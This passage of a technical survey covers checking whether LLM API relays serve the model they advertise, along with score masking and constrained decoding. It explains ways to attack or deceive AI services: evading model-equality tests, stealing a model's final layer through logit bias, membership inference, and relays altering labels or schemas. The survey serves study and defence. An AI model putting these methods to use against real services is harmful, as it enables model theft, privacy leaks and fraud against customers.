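Zhang, Jiang and colleagues (2026), in *Real Money, Fake Models*, audited shadow APIs, their term for relays that resell access to well-known models in restricted regions without documenting where they get it. Starting from code published with conference papers, the researchers found 17 such services, which 187 academic papers had used. They tested eight models on each of three popular services between September and December 2025.

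Their main test, LLMmap, compares a model's answers to a set of questions with those of known models. In 11 of the 24 cases (46%), the closest match was not the advertised model. Two services' "GPT-5" most resembled GLM-4-9B, a small open model. In three more cases the model matched, but its answers were unusually far from the official ones.

The researchers also ran LLMmap on six services of their own, where it wrongly flagged 3% of honest cases and missed 5% of substitutions. At that false-positive rate, chance would explain about one of the 11 mismatches. But a match with another model does not prove that the service was running it. In four of the 11 cases, the closest match was a larger or newer model from the same family, which may reflect errors in the test or careless routing rather than cost-cutting. The three services were not a random sample, and Zhang and colleagues do not extend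 the result to the other 14.

The most worrying result for a hospital involved a model that LLMmap identified correctly. Google's official Gemini-2.5-flash correctly answered 83.82% of the questions in MedQA, a set of US medical exam questions, compared with about 37% through each of the three shadow APIs. The researchers suspect that the services ran the genuine model but cut back its reasoning to save money. If so, a hospital that had tested the model with full reasoning was getting the right weights but less reasoning than it had tested.

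### Comparing samples of answers

A recipient can run statistical tests without the seller's help. The recipient puts the same questions to the suspect service and to a trusted reference many times, then checks whether the answers follow the same pattern. *Model Equality Testing* (Gao, Liang and Guestrin, 2024) treats this as the standard statistical problem of deciding whether two samples come from the same source.

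One test compares a sample of responses from the suspect service with a sample from the reference model. It measures the similarity of two responses by counting the positions at which they have the same token. It then adds the average similarity within each sample and subtracts twice the average similarity between the samples. Suppose each answer is a single word, treated as one token, and the reference returns "benign" 80% of the time and "malignant" 20%, while the suspect service returns them 60% and 40% of the time. With large samples, the result is about 0.68 + 0.52 − 2 × 0.56 = 0.08, whereas it would be about zero if the two distributions were identical.

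- Two reference answers agree with probability 0.8² + 0.2² = 0.68.
- Two suspect answers agree with probability 0.6² + 0.4² = 0.52.
- One answer from each agrees with probability 0.8 × 0.6 + 0.2 × 0.4 = 0.56.

The distance is 0.68 + 0.52 − 2 × 0.56 = 0.08. If the services were identical, it would differ from zero only by chance. To check whether chance could explain the result, the software can shuffle the answers between the two samples many times and count how often the distance is at least 0.08.

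The test had a median detection rate of 77.4% across compressed and otherwise altered models, at a false-alarm rate of 5%, using an average of ten responses to each of 25 prompts. In summer 2024, Gao and colleagues used it on 31 commercial offerings of Meta's Llama models, whose weights are public, and flagged 11. Each audit cost less than $1. A flag shows that the answers differ from those of Meta's weights, but the cause could be compression, deliberate changes or faulty software.

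In *Are You Getting What You Pay For?*, Cai, Shi and colleagues (2025) then examined how a dishonest seller could get past this and similar tests.

- **Compression.** With smaller models, the equality test detected an 8-bit version less than 20% of the time. Programs trained to recognise a model's style did no better than guessing.
- **Mixing.** When 20% of a larger model's responses came from its 8-bit version, the test detected this about as often as it raised false alarms.
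- **Recognising the test.** A seller can send well-known benchmark questions to the genuine model and everything else to a cheaper one.
- **False names.** Asking a model what it is doesn't help much, because the seller can instruct it to give another name.

Cai and colleagues found that the probabilities of individual tokens give stronger evidence, but a seller can simply withhold them.

Newer tests are cheaper. The test in *Is Your LLM Relay Serving What It Claims?* (Miao, Huang and colleagues, 2026) has a model pick from a short list of items such as numbers, letters or colours. Models choose some options more often than others, and these tendencies differ even between models from the same company. Asking five such questions 50 times each cost less than 5 US cents for each of the four models priced. For all four, the test was right more than 99.5% of the time when the service ran either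 the advertised model or a full replacement.

However, the test cannot distinguish a different model from the same model with different settings. When Miao and colleagues added an instruction, such as to answer in JSON, to a genuine DeepSeek model, the test flagged it at least 99% of the time. A relay could also evade the test by recognising its odd questions and passing them to the genuine model.

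Partial substitution raises the number of requests a tester needs. Suppose the seller replaces a share ε of the responses, and the test detects each replacement with probability q. The chance that m requests detect no replacement is (1 − εq)^m, so a tester who accepts a 5% chance of missing the substitution needs about 3/(εq) requests. *Which Model Is Actually Serving You?* (2026) measured q = 0.42 for a 4-bit version of a small Qwen model when the question left room for varied answers. If the seller replaces 10% of responses, the tester needs about 72 requests. With a less suitable question, q was only 0.06, barely above the false-alarm rate.

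*API-TAIL* (2026), from TokenRhythm Technologies, deals with both partial substitution and changed settings. It uses a local copy of the advertised model to measure how surprising each response is. Honest changes of settings tend to shift all the scores together, while a substitute adds a few responses that stand out. With 200 requests, the method detected a 10% substitution at least 69% of the time in 13 of 16 test conditions. Two older tests, including an adapted version of Gao's, detected none in the conditions where the company compared them. But the new method also detected none in one condition, where the substitute was the previous release of the same Qwen model.

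All these tests judge a service over many requests. None can establish which model wrote a particular patient's diagnosis.

### Rerunning part of the work

A verifier with a copy of the weights can rerun the model and compare its internal values with the seller's. An exact comparison usually fails even when the seller is honest, because computers round numbers and the result depends on the order of the additions. Suppose a machine keeps three significant digits. It computes (100 + 0.4) + 0.4 as 100, because each 0.4 is lost to rounding, but 100 + (0.4 + 0.4) as 101. The order in which a GPU adds numbers depends on its design, its software and how many requests it is handling at once.

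These small differences can change the text. *Fingerprinting Inference Systems of Large Language Models* (2026) asked one model a yes-or-no question about the 1966 football World Cup on three systems. The scores differed on all three, and the predicted answer flipped on one of them. *Accelerating the Mitigation of LLM Inference Nondeterminism Across GPU Architectures* (2026) cites an earlier study in which accuracy on a mathematics test varied by up to 9% across 12 hardware and software setups.

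*TOPLOC* (Ong, Di Ferrante and colleagues, 2025) describes a fingerprint that tolerates rounding because it uses only the model's largest internal values, which rounding affects least.

1. After every 32 tokens, the provider takes the 128 largest values in the model's last layer, along with their positions.
2. It encodes them as a polynomial that passes through all 128 points. This takes 258 bytes, about a thousandth of the space that the full set of values would need.
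3. The verifier feeds the prompt and the finished response through its own copy of the model. This is much faster than generating the response, because the model can process all the tokens at once.
4. The verifier compares its values with the provider's, and accepts if no more than 38 of the 128 exponents differ and the differences in the fractions are small.

When the provider and verifier ran the same model on different GPUs or with different software, at most 28 exponents differed. At least 67 differed when the provider secretly added an instruction to the prompt, and at least 125 when it used another model. The method made no errors in these tests, but Ong and colleagues chose the limits after seeing some of the same measurements. The margin between 16-bit and 8-bit versions of a model was also small.

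A more basic weakness is that the fingerprint does not show who or what wrote the text. A seller could let a cheap model write "benign", or type it by hand, and then run the advertised model over the finished text to produce a valid fingerprint. In *DiFR*, Karvonen, Reuter and colleagues (2025) argue that having to run the genuine model removes most of the financial motive for cheating. But they report that processing finished text is often three to five times faster than generating it, so the seller might still save money. The cost would not deter an attacker who wants to change the diagnosis.

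Their own method, Token-DiFR, also checks how the software chose each token. Common software adds a random number to each token's score and picks the highest total. A starting value called the seed determines the random numbers, so a verifier who knows the seed can repeat the choice. In the earlier example, the model gave "malignant" a probability of 0.93 and "benign" 0.07, so "malignant" leads by about 2.6 in score. If the random numbers are 0.2 for "malignant" and 0.9 for "benign", "malignant" still wins by 1.9. Rounding can change the result of a near tie, but if the response contains "benign" despite a gap this large, the verifier has reason to be suspicious.

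In tests by Karvonen and colleagues, the provider's and verifier's tokens agreed more than 98% of the time. The method detected 4-bit compression almost perfectly within 300 tokens. Detecting subtler changes took thousands of tokens, and for one model on mixed hardware the standard version could not reliably detect a temperature of 1.1 in place of 1.0. A second method, which compares compressed internal values, needed two tokens to detect 4-bit compression, but like TOPLOC it does not check who chose the tokens.

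Other researchers are trying to remove the rounding differences. *Bit-Exact AI Inference Verification Without Performance Tradeoffs* (2026) found that two widely used programs give identical results on NVIDIA GPUs under the same conditions, with rare exceptions. A verifier who can recreate those conditions could therefore demand an exact match. *Accelerating the Mitigation of LLM Inference Nondeterminism Across GPU Architectures* describes software that makes the main calculations identical even across different GPU designs.

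### Zero-knowledge proofs

Few commercial developers will give a hospital their weights, but a zero-knowledge proof lets the hospital check which model produced a response without seeing them. The provider first publishes a commitment, a short value that fixes the weights without revealing them. For each response, it produces a proof that the committed weights give the claimed result for the hospital's input. A provider that used other weights has only a negligible chance of passing the hospital's check.

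The proof shows only that the provider used the model it committed to. A provider could commit to a cheap model and sell it under an expensive model's name, and every proof would still be valid. Someone the hospital trusts therefore has to test the committed model. The proof should also cover the choice of each token, or it leaves the same gap as TOPLOC.

The main obstacle is speed. *Towards Verifiable AI with Lightweight Cryptographic Proofs of Inference* (2026) timed zkLLM, a 2024 system, and *Bits Under ZK-LLM* (2026) timed proofs for the small GPT-2 models. *zkLLMPoT* (2026) proves how a model was trained, which includes proving a run of the model over a text. The measurements use different hardware and cover different amounts of work, so the table shows only rough magnitudes.

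| Model | Work proved | Time to produce the proof | Reported by |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama-2-7B | One token | 2,646 seconds | Karvonen and colleagues, citing a 2025 system |
| Llama-2-7B | One inference with zkLLM | 388 seconds | *Towards Verifiable AI with Lightweight Cryptographic Proofs of Inference* |
| GPT-2 Small | 16 tokens, on ordinary processors | 104 seconds | *Bits Under ZK-LLM* |
| GPT-2 Large | 16 tokens, on ordinary processors | 526 seconds | *Bits Under ZK-LLM* |
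| 0.125 billion parameters | 512 tokens, main operations | 16 seconds | *zkLLMPoT* |
| 13 billion parameters | 512 tokens, main operations | 131 seconds | *zkLLMPoT* |

Checking a proof is much faster than producing one, and takes 2.36 seconds for zkLLM. Ong and colleagues estimated that zkLLM would need weeks to prove a 2,000-token response from a 13-billion-parameter model, but they multiplied the time for one run by the number of tokens. A single proof over the finished text may cover all the tokens, so the actual time is probably far shorter. Even two minutes is a long wait for an agent that makes dozens of calls, though a hospital might accept it for a diagnosis.

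A provider can save time by proving only a sample of its work. In *Seal, Then Sample* (2026), the provider first fixes a record of the whole calculation, then proves randomly chosen parts of it. In one reported run, it proved five of 163 parts. Fixing the record and proving those parts took 21 minutes, but producing the record had taken 13.5 hours. A random sample of five has a 5/163 chance, or about 3%, of catching a provider that falsified just one part, and will always catch one that falsified every part.

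*Towards Verifiable AI with Lightweight Cryptographic Proofs of Inference* also proposes a sampling method that takes milliseconds, but each proof reveals some of the model's weights.

### The checks compared

The choice depends largely on how much the seller will cooperate. (A seller willing to run the model in an attested enclave can offer evidence for each response at a much lower cost than a zero-knowledge proof, but the hospital then has to trust the hardware.)

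| Check | Who must cooperate | Cost | What it catches | What it covers |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Statistical tests | Nobody, but the tester needs a trusted reference | From under a cent to about $1 per audit, plus computing time for some tests | Full substitution, and some compression and mixing | A service over many requests |
| TOPLOC | The provider, and the verifier needs the weights | 8 bytes per token and one run over the finished text | A different model or prompt, but not text written elsewhere | A single response |
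| Token-DiFR | The provider must share the seed, and the verifier needs the weights | One run over the finished text | Compression, and faults in choosing tokens | Hundreds to thousands of tokens, so one long response or several |
| Zero-knowledge proof | The provider | Minutes or more of computing per response | Any departure from the part of the calculation it covers | A single response |

For models with public weights, a customer can use a form of Token-DiFR without the provider's help by setting the temperature to zero, so that generation uses no random numbers. This works as a spot check, but the provider could treat temperature-zero requests differently from the rest.

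All four checks compare the response with what the stated model would produce, so they cannot show whether it is right about the patient's condition. The official Gemini-2.5-flash got about 16% of the MedQA questions wrong, and a perfect proof would have confirmed that those wrong answers came from the model. A substitute can also do nearly as well as the real model. On GPQA, a test of graduate-level science, Zhang and colleagues measured accuracies of 44.61% for GPT-4o-mini and 42.93% for Qwen2.5-7B, which one shadow API appeared to be serving instead of GPT-4o-mini.

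## What does hiding confidence scores protect?

Hiding confidence scores protects a model and its training data from people who study its outputs, but it does not stop anyone from changing a prediction. The scores are the probabilities a classifier assigns to the possible answers, and its prediction, called the label, is the answer with the highest score.

Suppose the hospital's model sorts scans into five categories. The table shows the scores for one scan under each form of score masking and what a dishonest relay could deliver instead.

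| Form of masking | What the provider sends | What the relay could deliver |
|---|---|---|
| None | malignant 0.5137, benign 0.4312, inflammation 0.0391, cyst 0.0117, scar 0.0043 | benign 0.5137, malignant 0.4312, the rest unchanged |
| Top two scores only | malignant 0.5137, benign 0.4312 | benign 0.5137, malignant 0.4312 |
| Rounding to one decimal | malignant 0.5, benign 0.4, the rest 0.0 | benign 0.5, malignant 0.4, the rest 0.0 |
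| Added noise | malignant 0.5737, benign 0.3812, inflammation 0.0191, cyst 0.0217, scar 0.0043 | benign 0.5737, malignant 0.3812, the rest unchanged |
| Label alone | malignant | benign |

The relay only has to swap two words, and every forged output looks normal. A signature on what the provider sends would expose the change in all five cases, with or without masking. Noise makes it harder to check integrity by rerunning the model, because a verifier cannot reproduce the scores without knowing the noise.

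### What attackers learn from scores

An attacker searching for an image that fools the model can change a few pixels and see the score for "malignant" fall from 0.5137 to 0.5129. The attacker then knows that the change helped and can continue in that direction. If the model returned only the label, the attacker would see "malignant" both times. Scores also help someone who trains a copy of the model on its answers, because a probability for each class contains more information than the label alone.

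Membership inference also uses scores, because models tend to be more confident about examples they were trained on. *Label-Only Membership Inference Attacks* (Choquette-Choo, Tramèr and colleagues, 2020) gives the example of a model that predicts how cancer patients react to a drug. Learning that someone's record is in its training data reveals that the person has cancer.

### MemGuard

*MemGuard* (Jia, Salem and colleagues, 2019) proposes a defence against attackers who train a second classifier to guess from the scores whether a record was in the training data. Small, carefully chosen changes to the input can fool this classifier like any other, so MemGuard makes such changes to the scores before sending them.

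The defender does not know which classifier the attacker uses, and therefore trains its own. Let s be the true scores, n the noise, and g(s + n) the probability of "member" according to the defender's classifier. MemGuard picks the noise at random, in a way that brings the average of g(s + n) as close as possible to 0.5, subject to these constraints:

- arg maxⱼ (sⱼ + nⱼ) = arg maxⱼ sⱼ, so the label does not change.
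- E[Σⱼ |nⱼ|] ≤ ε, so the total change to the scores is, on average, within a budget ε.
- sⱼ + nⱼ ≥ 0 for every j, and Σⱼ (sⱼ + nⱼ) = 1, so the results are still probabilities.

This problem is hard to solve exactly. MemGuard approximates the solution by looking for the smallest noise r that brings g to about 0.5 without changing the label. If R is the total change that r makes, MemGuard adds r with probability min(ε/R, 1) and otherwise sends the true scores. The noise in the table has R = 0.06 + 0.05 + 0.02 + 0.01 = 0.14, so with a budget of ε = 0.07 MemGuard would add it half the time. MemGuard must make the same choice every time someone submits the same scan, or an attacker could work out the true scores by submitting it repeatedly.

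The label constraint gives a limited integrity guarantee, because the masking itself never changes a diagnosis. Jia and colleagues wanted this because changing even 1% of labels may be intolerable in healthcare or finance. The budget guarantees less, because it limits only the average change to the scores. In the example, a doctor who receives the noisy scores sees twice the budgeted change, and the diagnosis looks more certain than it is.

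### Label-only attacks

Choquette-Choo and colleagues call defences like MemGuard "confidence masking", and showed that an attacker can get around them by ignoring the scores. In the simplest label-only attack, the attacker guesses that a record was in the training data if the model classifies it correctly. When half the tested records come from the training data, this guess is right with probability

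1/2 + (training accuracy − test accuracy)/2.

For a model that classifies 100% of its training examples and 60% of new ones correctly, the attack succeeds 70% of the time.

A better attack measures how far a record can change before its label does, because training examples tend to keep their labels under larger changes. In a simple linear model with two labels, the distance from a record to the point where the label flips is σ⁻¹(p)/‖w‖, where p is the score, w is the list of weights, and σ converts the model's raw result into a probability. This distance gives the same information as the score. The researchers expected much the same to hold for neural networks. For images, they shifted and rotated the picture or searched for the nearest image with a different label. For other data, they used 10,000 queries to check how often the label stayed the same after random changes.

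The table shows how often each attack was right on four sets of non-image data, where guessing would be right 50% of the time.

| Data | Simplest label-only attack | Score-based attack, no defence | Score-based attack, MemGuard | Random-change attack, with or without MemGuard |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Texas | 73.9% | 84.0% | 50.0% | 80.3% |
| Purchase | 67.1% | 86.1% | 50.0% | 87.4% |
| Location | 72.1% | 92.6% | 50.0% | 89.2% |
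| Adult | 58.7% | 59.9% | 50.0% | 58.7% |

MemGuard reduced the score-based attack to guessing (50.0%) but had no effect on the label-only attacks. The 50.0% was misleading even as a measure of what the scores revealed, because the researchers who reported such results had tuned their attacks on models without MemGuard. On the Adult dataset, no attack did much better than guessing, with or without a defence.

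About 2,500 queries per record, at a cost of about $0.25, were enough to match the score-based attack on one set of images. However, the experiments used small training sets, which make models overfit heavily, and assumed that the attacker knew the model's design and had similar data. *OSLO* (2024) reports that the earlier label-only attacks found few members when false accusations had to be rare, and proposes an attack that needs only one query.

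Two defences substantially reduced the leak, and both change the training instead of the output. Differentially private training adds noise so that no single record has much influence on the model, and strong L2 regularisation penalises large weights. Both made the models less accurate, although accuracy fell less when training started from a model already trained on other data.

### Stealing a layer through the top five scores

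A language model calculates each token's probability from a raw score called a logit. Some providers return the logarithms of the highest probabilities, known as logprobs. In *Stealing Part of a Production Language Model*, Carlini, Paleka and colleagues (2024) recovered the last layer of two commercial models from the top five logprobs.

The last layer computes the logits from a much shorter list of internal numbers, so the logits cannot all vary independently. Suppose a tiny model has two internal numbers, a and b, and three tokens with logits a, b and a + b. An outsider who sees the logits (2, 3, 5), (1, 4, 5) and (6, 1, 7) can work out that the third is always the sum of the first two, and therefore that the model has only two internal numbers. With thousands of complete lists of logits, an outsider can use the same reasoning to find how many internal numbers a real model has, as well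 as the weights of its last layer up to an unknown change of coordinates.

OpenAI's interface did not return complete lists, but it let users add a "logit bias" to chosen tokens to make them more or less likely. The researchers added a large bias B to four tokens at a time, which moved them into the top five beside the token that normally came first. If zᵢ is the logit of a boosted token, z₁ that of the usual first token, and yᵢ and y₁ their returned logprobs, then

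zᵢ − z₁ = yᵢ − y₁ − B.

Each query reveals four logits relative to z₁, so a vocabulary of 100,000 tokens takes 25,000 queries per complete list.

The attack recovered the last layers of OpenAI's ada and babbage models for about $4 and $12, and showed that their hidden dimensions were 1,024 and 2,048. It also found the exact hidden dimension of GPT-3.5 Turbo, which OpenAI confirmed but asked the researchers not to publish. Finlayson, Ren and Swayamdipta (2024) independently used the same idea in *Logits of API-Protected LLMs Leak Proprietary Information*. They measured about 4,600 for GPT-3.5 Turbo and inferred a true value of 4,096, because hidden dimensions are usually powers of two. The last layer is only a small part of a model, and Carlini and colleagues saw no immediate practical consequences from recovering it.

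Withholding logprobs means this attack needs more queries, but does not prevent it. An attacker can raise a token's bias until it becomes the model's first choice, and the bias required reveals the difference between the two tokens' logits. The best version of this method took 3.7 queries per logit, compared with 0.25 when logprobs were available. Removing the logit bias would have stopped all the known attacks, but developers use it to block unwanted words. After Carlini and colleagues reported the problem, OpenAI and Google changed their interfaces to prevent the attack or make it more expensive. The paper's suggestions included forbidding logit bias and logprobs in the same request.

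### Who still returns probabilities?

Most services now return no probabilities. Chauvin, Le Merrer and colleagues requested them from 710 working services on OpenRouter and received them from 164, or 23% (*Log Probability Tracking of LLM APIs*, 2025). Those services returned 5 to 20 probabilities per token. *Echoes within the Reasoning* (2026) later surveyed commercial interfaces and also found that 20 was a common limit.

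*Rethinking Verbalized Confidence for LLM-as-a-Judge* (Hsiao, 2026) reports that, of the three leading model families, only OpenAI's GPT still returns logprobs. Claude never did, and Gemini returned them in version 2.5 Pro but not in 3.1 Pro. The newest GPT model in the comparison was GPT-5.4. OpenAI's support also has gaps. A post on OpenAI's forum, *GPT 5.2 LogProbs support removed?*, quotes the error message "logprobs are not supported with reasoning models". In another post, *GPT-5.1/5.2*, a developer who had turned reasoning off received logprobs for ordinary text but an empty list when the answer had to follow a fixed format.

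Limiting the output to the top 20 logits does not stop all leaks. *What do your logits know?* (2026) used those logits to predict attributes that the user's question had not asked about, and did better than chance with as few as 100 examples.

### Users lose a warning

The scan in the first table was close to a tie. A doctor who sees only "malignant" can't distinguish it from a diagnosis with a score of 0.99, and so has no reason to ask for a second opinion. Rounding the scores to 0.5 and 0.4 still shows that they were close. The developer who received the empty list had similarly wanted logprobs to judge how far to trust each label.

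When a provider hides confidence scores, users can still ask the model how confident it is. Hsiao had models argue for both answers, warned them that they had been overconfident, and then asked for a confidence from 0 to 100. For Claude Sonnet 4.5, the average gap between stated confidence and actual accuracy was 3.8 percentage points with this method, compared with 8.9 with a plainer request. As tasks became more subjective, stated confidence from GPT-5.2 and GPT-5.4 matched human ratings more consistently than a logprob-based score did. The tasks were judging summaries and other model responses and checking claims against sources, so the results may not apply to diagnoses. Stated confidence may also give attackers some of the information the provider withheld.

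### Auditors lose a cheap test

Logprobs also help customers check whether a provider has changed its model. Chauvin and colleagues repeatedly sent services the letter "x", requested one token in reply, and compared the average logprobs over time. This detected changes as small as one step of additional training. Hourly checks would cost $0.14 a year at GPT-4.1 prices, compared with $146 for Gao's equality test, which uses only the text. The logprob test was also more accurate, giving a changed model a higher score than an unchanged one 91.5% of the time on average, compared with 67.0% for Gao's test.

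Over more than four months, the researchers monitored 189 services and found 37 suspected changes, 34 of them in models with public weights. They could not confirm any of the changes. Two of the providers they contacted declined to give details and two did not reply. Like Gao's test, their method can flag a suspected change but cannot identify its cause.

Finlayson and colleagues argued that providers might want to keep the leak they had found, because the relationships between a model's logits work as a signature that customers can use to identify the model. If the logits change but the relationships stay the same, the provider has probably changed a hidden instruction or retrained only part of the model. If the relationships change too, the last layer is different.

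Auditors have since found ways to detect model changes from text alone. Chauvin, Lalanne and colleagues (2026), in *Token-Efficient Change Detection in LLM APIs*, look for prompts on which two tokens are almost tied for first place. At a temperature of zero, even a tiny change to the model can make it consistently output one of the two. They find these prompts by sending random inputs three times each and keeping those that produce different answers. The method performs about as well as the best logprob tests and costs a thirtieth as much as other text-only tests. *API-TAIL* also uses only the text, and raised false alarms at most 6.9% of the time on each of 26 honest services.

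The tie-based method and the label-only attacks both infer hidden scores from cases where a small change alters the answer. Hiding scores therefore hinders auditors less than it did in 2025, but for much the same reason it also offers less protection against attackers.

### OWASP's advice

OWASP's *Input threats* recommends showing only as much confidence information as users need, by rounding scores, replacing them with broad ranges or leaving them out. Where confidence is essential, as in medical decision support or safety-critical decisions, it advises keeping the scores but reducing their detail by rounding or adding noise. In all cases, it recommends checking that the change does not harm the system's accuracy or purpose.

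OWASP acknowledges that attackers can still estimate hidden confidence scores by making small changes to the input, and that hiding scores does not fully prevent label-only membership inference. It also compares hiding scores to gradient masking, which hides how a model responds to small changes without making it harder to fool. OWASP calls gradient masking fragile when used alone.

The hospital falls under the medical exception. Rounding suits it better than noise, because a doctor who knows the rounding rule knows how far a rounded score can be from the true one. The provider should sign the score together with the label. Otherwise a relay could keep the label "malignant" but change the score from 0.5 to 0.9, and the doctor would not see that the diagnosis was in doubt.

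## What does blocking tokens during generation guarantee?

Token masking, also called constrained decoding, can guarantee the form of an output. For example, it can ensure that a drug order has the right fields, but not that the order is right for the patient. Engineers use it mainly so that other programs can read a model's output, because one missing quotation mark can make a JSON response unusable.

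Let p(t) be the model's probability for the next token t, and A the set of tokens after which the text can still grow into a permitted output. The masking software blocks every token outside A and rescales the rest:

q(t) = p(t) / Σᵤ p(u) if t is in A, with the sum over all tokens u in A, and q(t) = 0 otherwise.

The set A comes from a grammar, a list of rules that defines the permitted texts. Developers often write a schema instead, which describes the fields in a JSON object and their permitted values, and software translates it into a grammar. *Grammar-Constrained Decoding for Structured NLP Tasks without Finetuning* (2023) obtained A from an incremental parser, a program that reads unfinished text and returns the tokens that may come next. The method needs the model's probabilities for the whole vocabulary, so customers of commercial services could not apply it themselves. OpenAI, Google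 and Anthropic now offer structured output modes.

### One field, token by token

Suppose the hospital's schema permits an object with one field, `route`, whose value is "oral" or "iv" (into a vein). The probabilities below are invented.

| Text so far | Model's probabilities | After masking |
|---|---|---|
| (nothing) | `Take` 0.5, `{"` 0.4, `{` 0.1 | `{"` 0.8, `{` 0.2 |
| `{"` | `route` 0.9, `drug` 0.1 | `route` 1 |
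| `{"route` | `":"` 0.9, `s` 0.1 | `":"` 1 |
| `{"route":"` | `by` 0.5, `oral` 0.3, `iv` 0.2 | `oral` 0.6, `iv` 0.4 |
| `{"route":"oral` | `ly` 0.7, `"}` 0.3 | `"}` 1 |

The result is `{"route":"oral"}`, and the mask doesn't allow the token that ends the response until this point. The token `":"` in the third row shows why masking software is hard to write. It closes the field's name, adds the colon and opens the value, so it covers three units of the grammar, while other tokens cover only part of a unit.

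### The exact guarantee

If the masking code is correct and generation finishes, the output belongs to the permitted language. The mask allows a token only if the text can still be completed within that language, and it allows the response to end only when the text is complete.

In *Machine-Checked Grammar-Constrained Decoding*, Bhat, Dandu and colleagues (2026) used the proof checker Lean to prove that the mask in a method called GreatGramma is sound, meaning it never allows a token that leads to a dead end, and complete, meaning it never blocks a token that could lead to a permitted output. The proof assumes, among other things, that every single character is also a token and that the format ignores some whitespace character between its units. Python and YAML may not meet the second condition, because spaces there can carry meaning. Someone also has to supply a description of the format,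 and the proof does not check whether that description matches what the hospital intended.

The work exposed a bug in GreatGramma, the method introduced in *Flexible and Efficient Grammar-Constrained Decoding* (2025). For a pattern that permits "a", "aba", "ababa" and so on, the software could end the response after "ab", which the pattern doesn't permit. The GreatGramma paper had reported that other tools often crash or produce incorrect outputs.

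Generation may also fail to finish. *Constrained Adaptive Rejection Sampling* (Parys, Vaidya and colleagues, 2025) notes that a masked model can keep opening brackets without ever closing them. OpenAI's *Structured Outputs* warns that if the prompt does not ask for JSON, its simpler JSON mode can produce whitespace until the response reaches the token limit.

A response that stops at the token limit may break the format. A truncated JSON object is easy to detect because it lacks its closing brace. But if the format is a bare number, a response cut off after the "5" of "50" is still a valid number. The hospital's software should therefore also check that the finish reason is not the token limit.

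Refusals are another exception. OpenAI returns them in a separate field because they may not fit the schema. Output constraints can also weaken a model's refusals, since a strict format may leave the model no way to decline.

### Schemas that the software cannot enforce

JSON Schema has dozens of features, and masking software supports only some of them. In *JSONSchemaBench*, Geng, Cooper and colleagues (2025) collected 9,558 schemas from real software and tested six masking systems. The table shows the percentage of all schemas that each system accepted, and the percentage of all schemas for which it then produced a valid output. It covers function calls and a harder set with 100 to 500 fields per schema.

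| System | Function calls: accepted | Function calls: valid output | Hard set: accepted | Hard set: valid output |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| No masking | 100% | 90% | 100% | 13% |
| Guidance | 98% | 96% | 60% | 41% |
| llama.cpp | 98% | 95% | 61% | 39% |
| XGrammar | 100% | 93% | 69% | 28% |
| Outlines | 99% | 95% | 47% | 3% |
| OpenAI | 89% | 89% | 9% | 9% |
| Gemini | 86% | 86% | Under 1% | Not reported |

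The gap between the two columns includes timeouts as well as invalid outputs, because a system also failed if it took more than 40 seconds. Timeouts explain most of Outlines' poor result. The valid-output figures are not directly comparable either, because OpenAI and Gemini ran their own models while the open systems ran a small Llama model. Still, OpenAI's approach was clearly different, since it rejected most of the hard schemas but produced valid output for the ones it accepted.

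That approach is safer for the hospital, because a system that accepts a schema and ignores part of it gives no sign that the guarantee is incomplete. Geng and colleagues call such a system under-constrained, and one that blocks valid outputs over-constrained. On an official test suite with 43 categories of features, XGrammar let through at least one invalid output in 38 categories, and Guidance did so in only one. Guidance refused to process schemas more often than XGrammar did.

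The systems in that test date from late 2024. OpenAI now supports text patterns, limits on numbers and limits on the length of lists, which it did not support then, and it still returns an error if a strict schema uses an unsupported feature. But some other systems still fail to enforce parts of a schema without returning an error. *DConstrain* (2026) examined 305 schemas that its own software could not process. A recent version of XGrammar accepted 298 of them, and for 124 it would allow a complete text that broke the original schema. For example, one schema required a value to match exactly one of several types, including integer and number, but XGrammar allowed 0, which is both. These schemas were unusually difficult, so the share is weak evidence about ordinary ones. Databricks' *Structured outputs* states that its service does not enforce limits on length or size.

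Rejecting a schema can mean losing valid output that a model would have produced from a prompt alone. In *ExtractBench* (2026), the structured modes of all three providers rejected a schema for CVs, but models given the schema in the prompt produced valid output in 26 of 42 attempts. In *ScrapeGraphAI-100k* (2026), limits on size or compilation caused 132 of the 245 genuine schema rejections.

The hospital can protect itself by using a separate program to check the finished output against the original schema. This check doesn't require trusting the provider, and it also works on a response that has passed through a relay. Masking then mainly saves the hospital from repeating failed requests.

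### Valid outputs that are wrong or harmful

The mask in the example would also allow "iv" for a patient who needs a tablet. *The Structured Output Benchmark* (2026) found that nearly all models can produce valid JSON, but the best model got only 83.0% of the values right when extracting them from text, 67.2% from images and 23.7% from audio.

Masking can introduce an error. Geng and colleagues give a hypothetical example in which a model is about to write "89,000" in a field that permits only digits. The mask blocks the comma, so the model has to continue in a way it otherwise would not and writes "890000", which meets the digits-only rule but is ten times too large.

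A valid output can also do damage. *Constrained Decoding for Diffusion Language Models via Efficient Inference over Finite Automata* (2026) warns that its masking method could help produce well-formed but malicious tool calls and database queries. A schema can exclude some of these, for instance by capping a dose at 10 mg. If the hospital checked the output against the schema again on arrival, it would also catch a relay that changed 5 mg to 50 mg, but not one that changed it to 10 mg.

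Anyone who controls the schema has considerable control over the answer. Suppose a relay edits the hospital's request so that the schema permits only "benign". The genuine model then returns "benign" for every scan. Only a signature that also covers the request, as in sign-c, would reveal the change.

### Masking changes the odds

Suppose a response begins with token A with probability 0.6 or token B with probability 0.4. If the model then continues freely, it produces a valid ending 10% of the time after A and 90% of the time after B.

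- A valid response that begins with A has probability 0.6 × 0.1 = 0.06.
- A valid response that begins with B has probability 0.4 × 0.9 = 0.36.

Valid responses have a total probability of 0.42, so among them A should have probability 0.06/0.42, or about 0.14. Masking leaves A's probability at 0.6 because both tokens can lead to a valid output, and the mask therefore allows both. If the software picks A, the mask then forces the model to produce one of the few valid endings.

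In the hospital, A might be "benign" and B "malignant", in a format that permits only a single word. Without the mask, the model usually follows "benign" with "but repeat the scan". The mask removes that warning, so the doctor reads a plain "benign" 60% of the time. A rate of 14% would not obviously serve the doctor better, since the model does lean towards "benign". A schema with a field for comments would avoid the problem.

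Park, Wang and colleagues (2024) measured this distortion in *Grammar-Aligned Decoding*, using a small grammar that permits only 00000 and five-digit binary strings starting with 1. They asked Mixtral for a binary string ending in 1. Without a mask, about 90% of its strings ended in 1. With the mask, only 30% did, because about half the time the model began with 0 and could then only write 00000.

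### Grammar-aligned decoding and its successors

The correct probability of a token depends on c(t), the chance that the model, continuing freely after t, would end with a valid output:

q*(t) = p(t)c(t) / Σᵤ p(u)c(u).

With c(A) = 0.1 and c(B) = 0.9, this gives the 0.14 above. Ordinary masking in effect replaces every c above zero with 1. Nobody can compute c exactly for a realistic model, because that would mean adding up the probabilities of all possible continuations.

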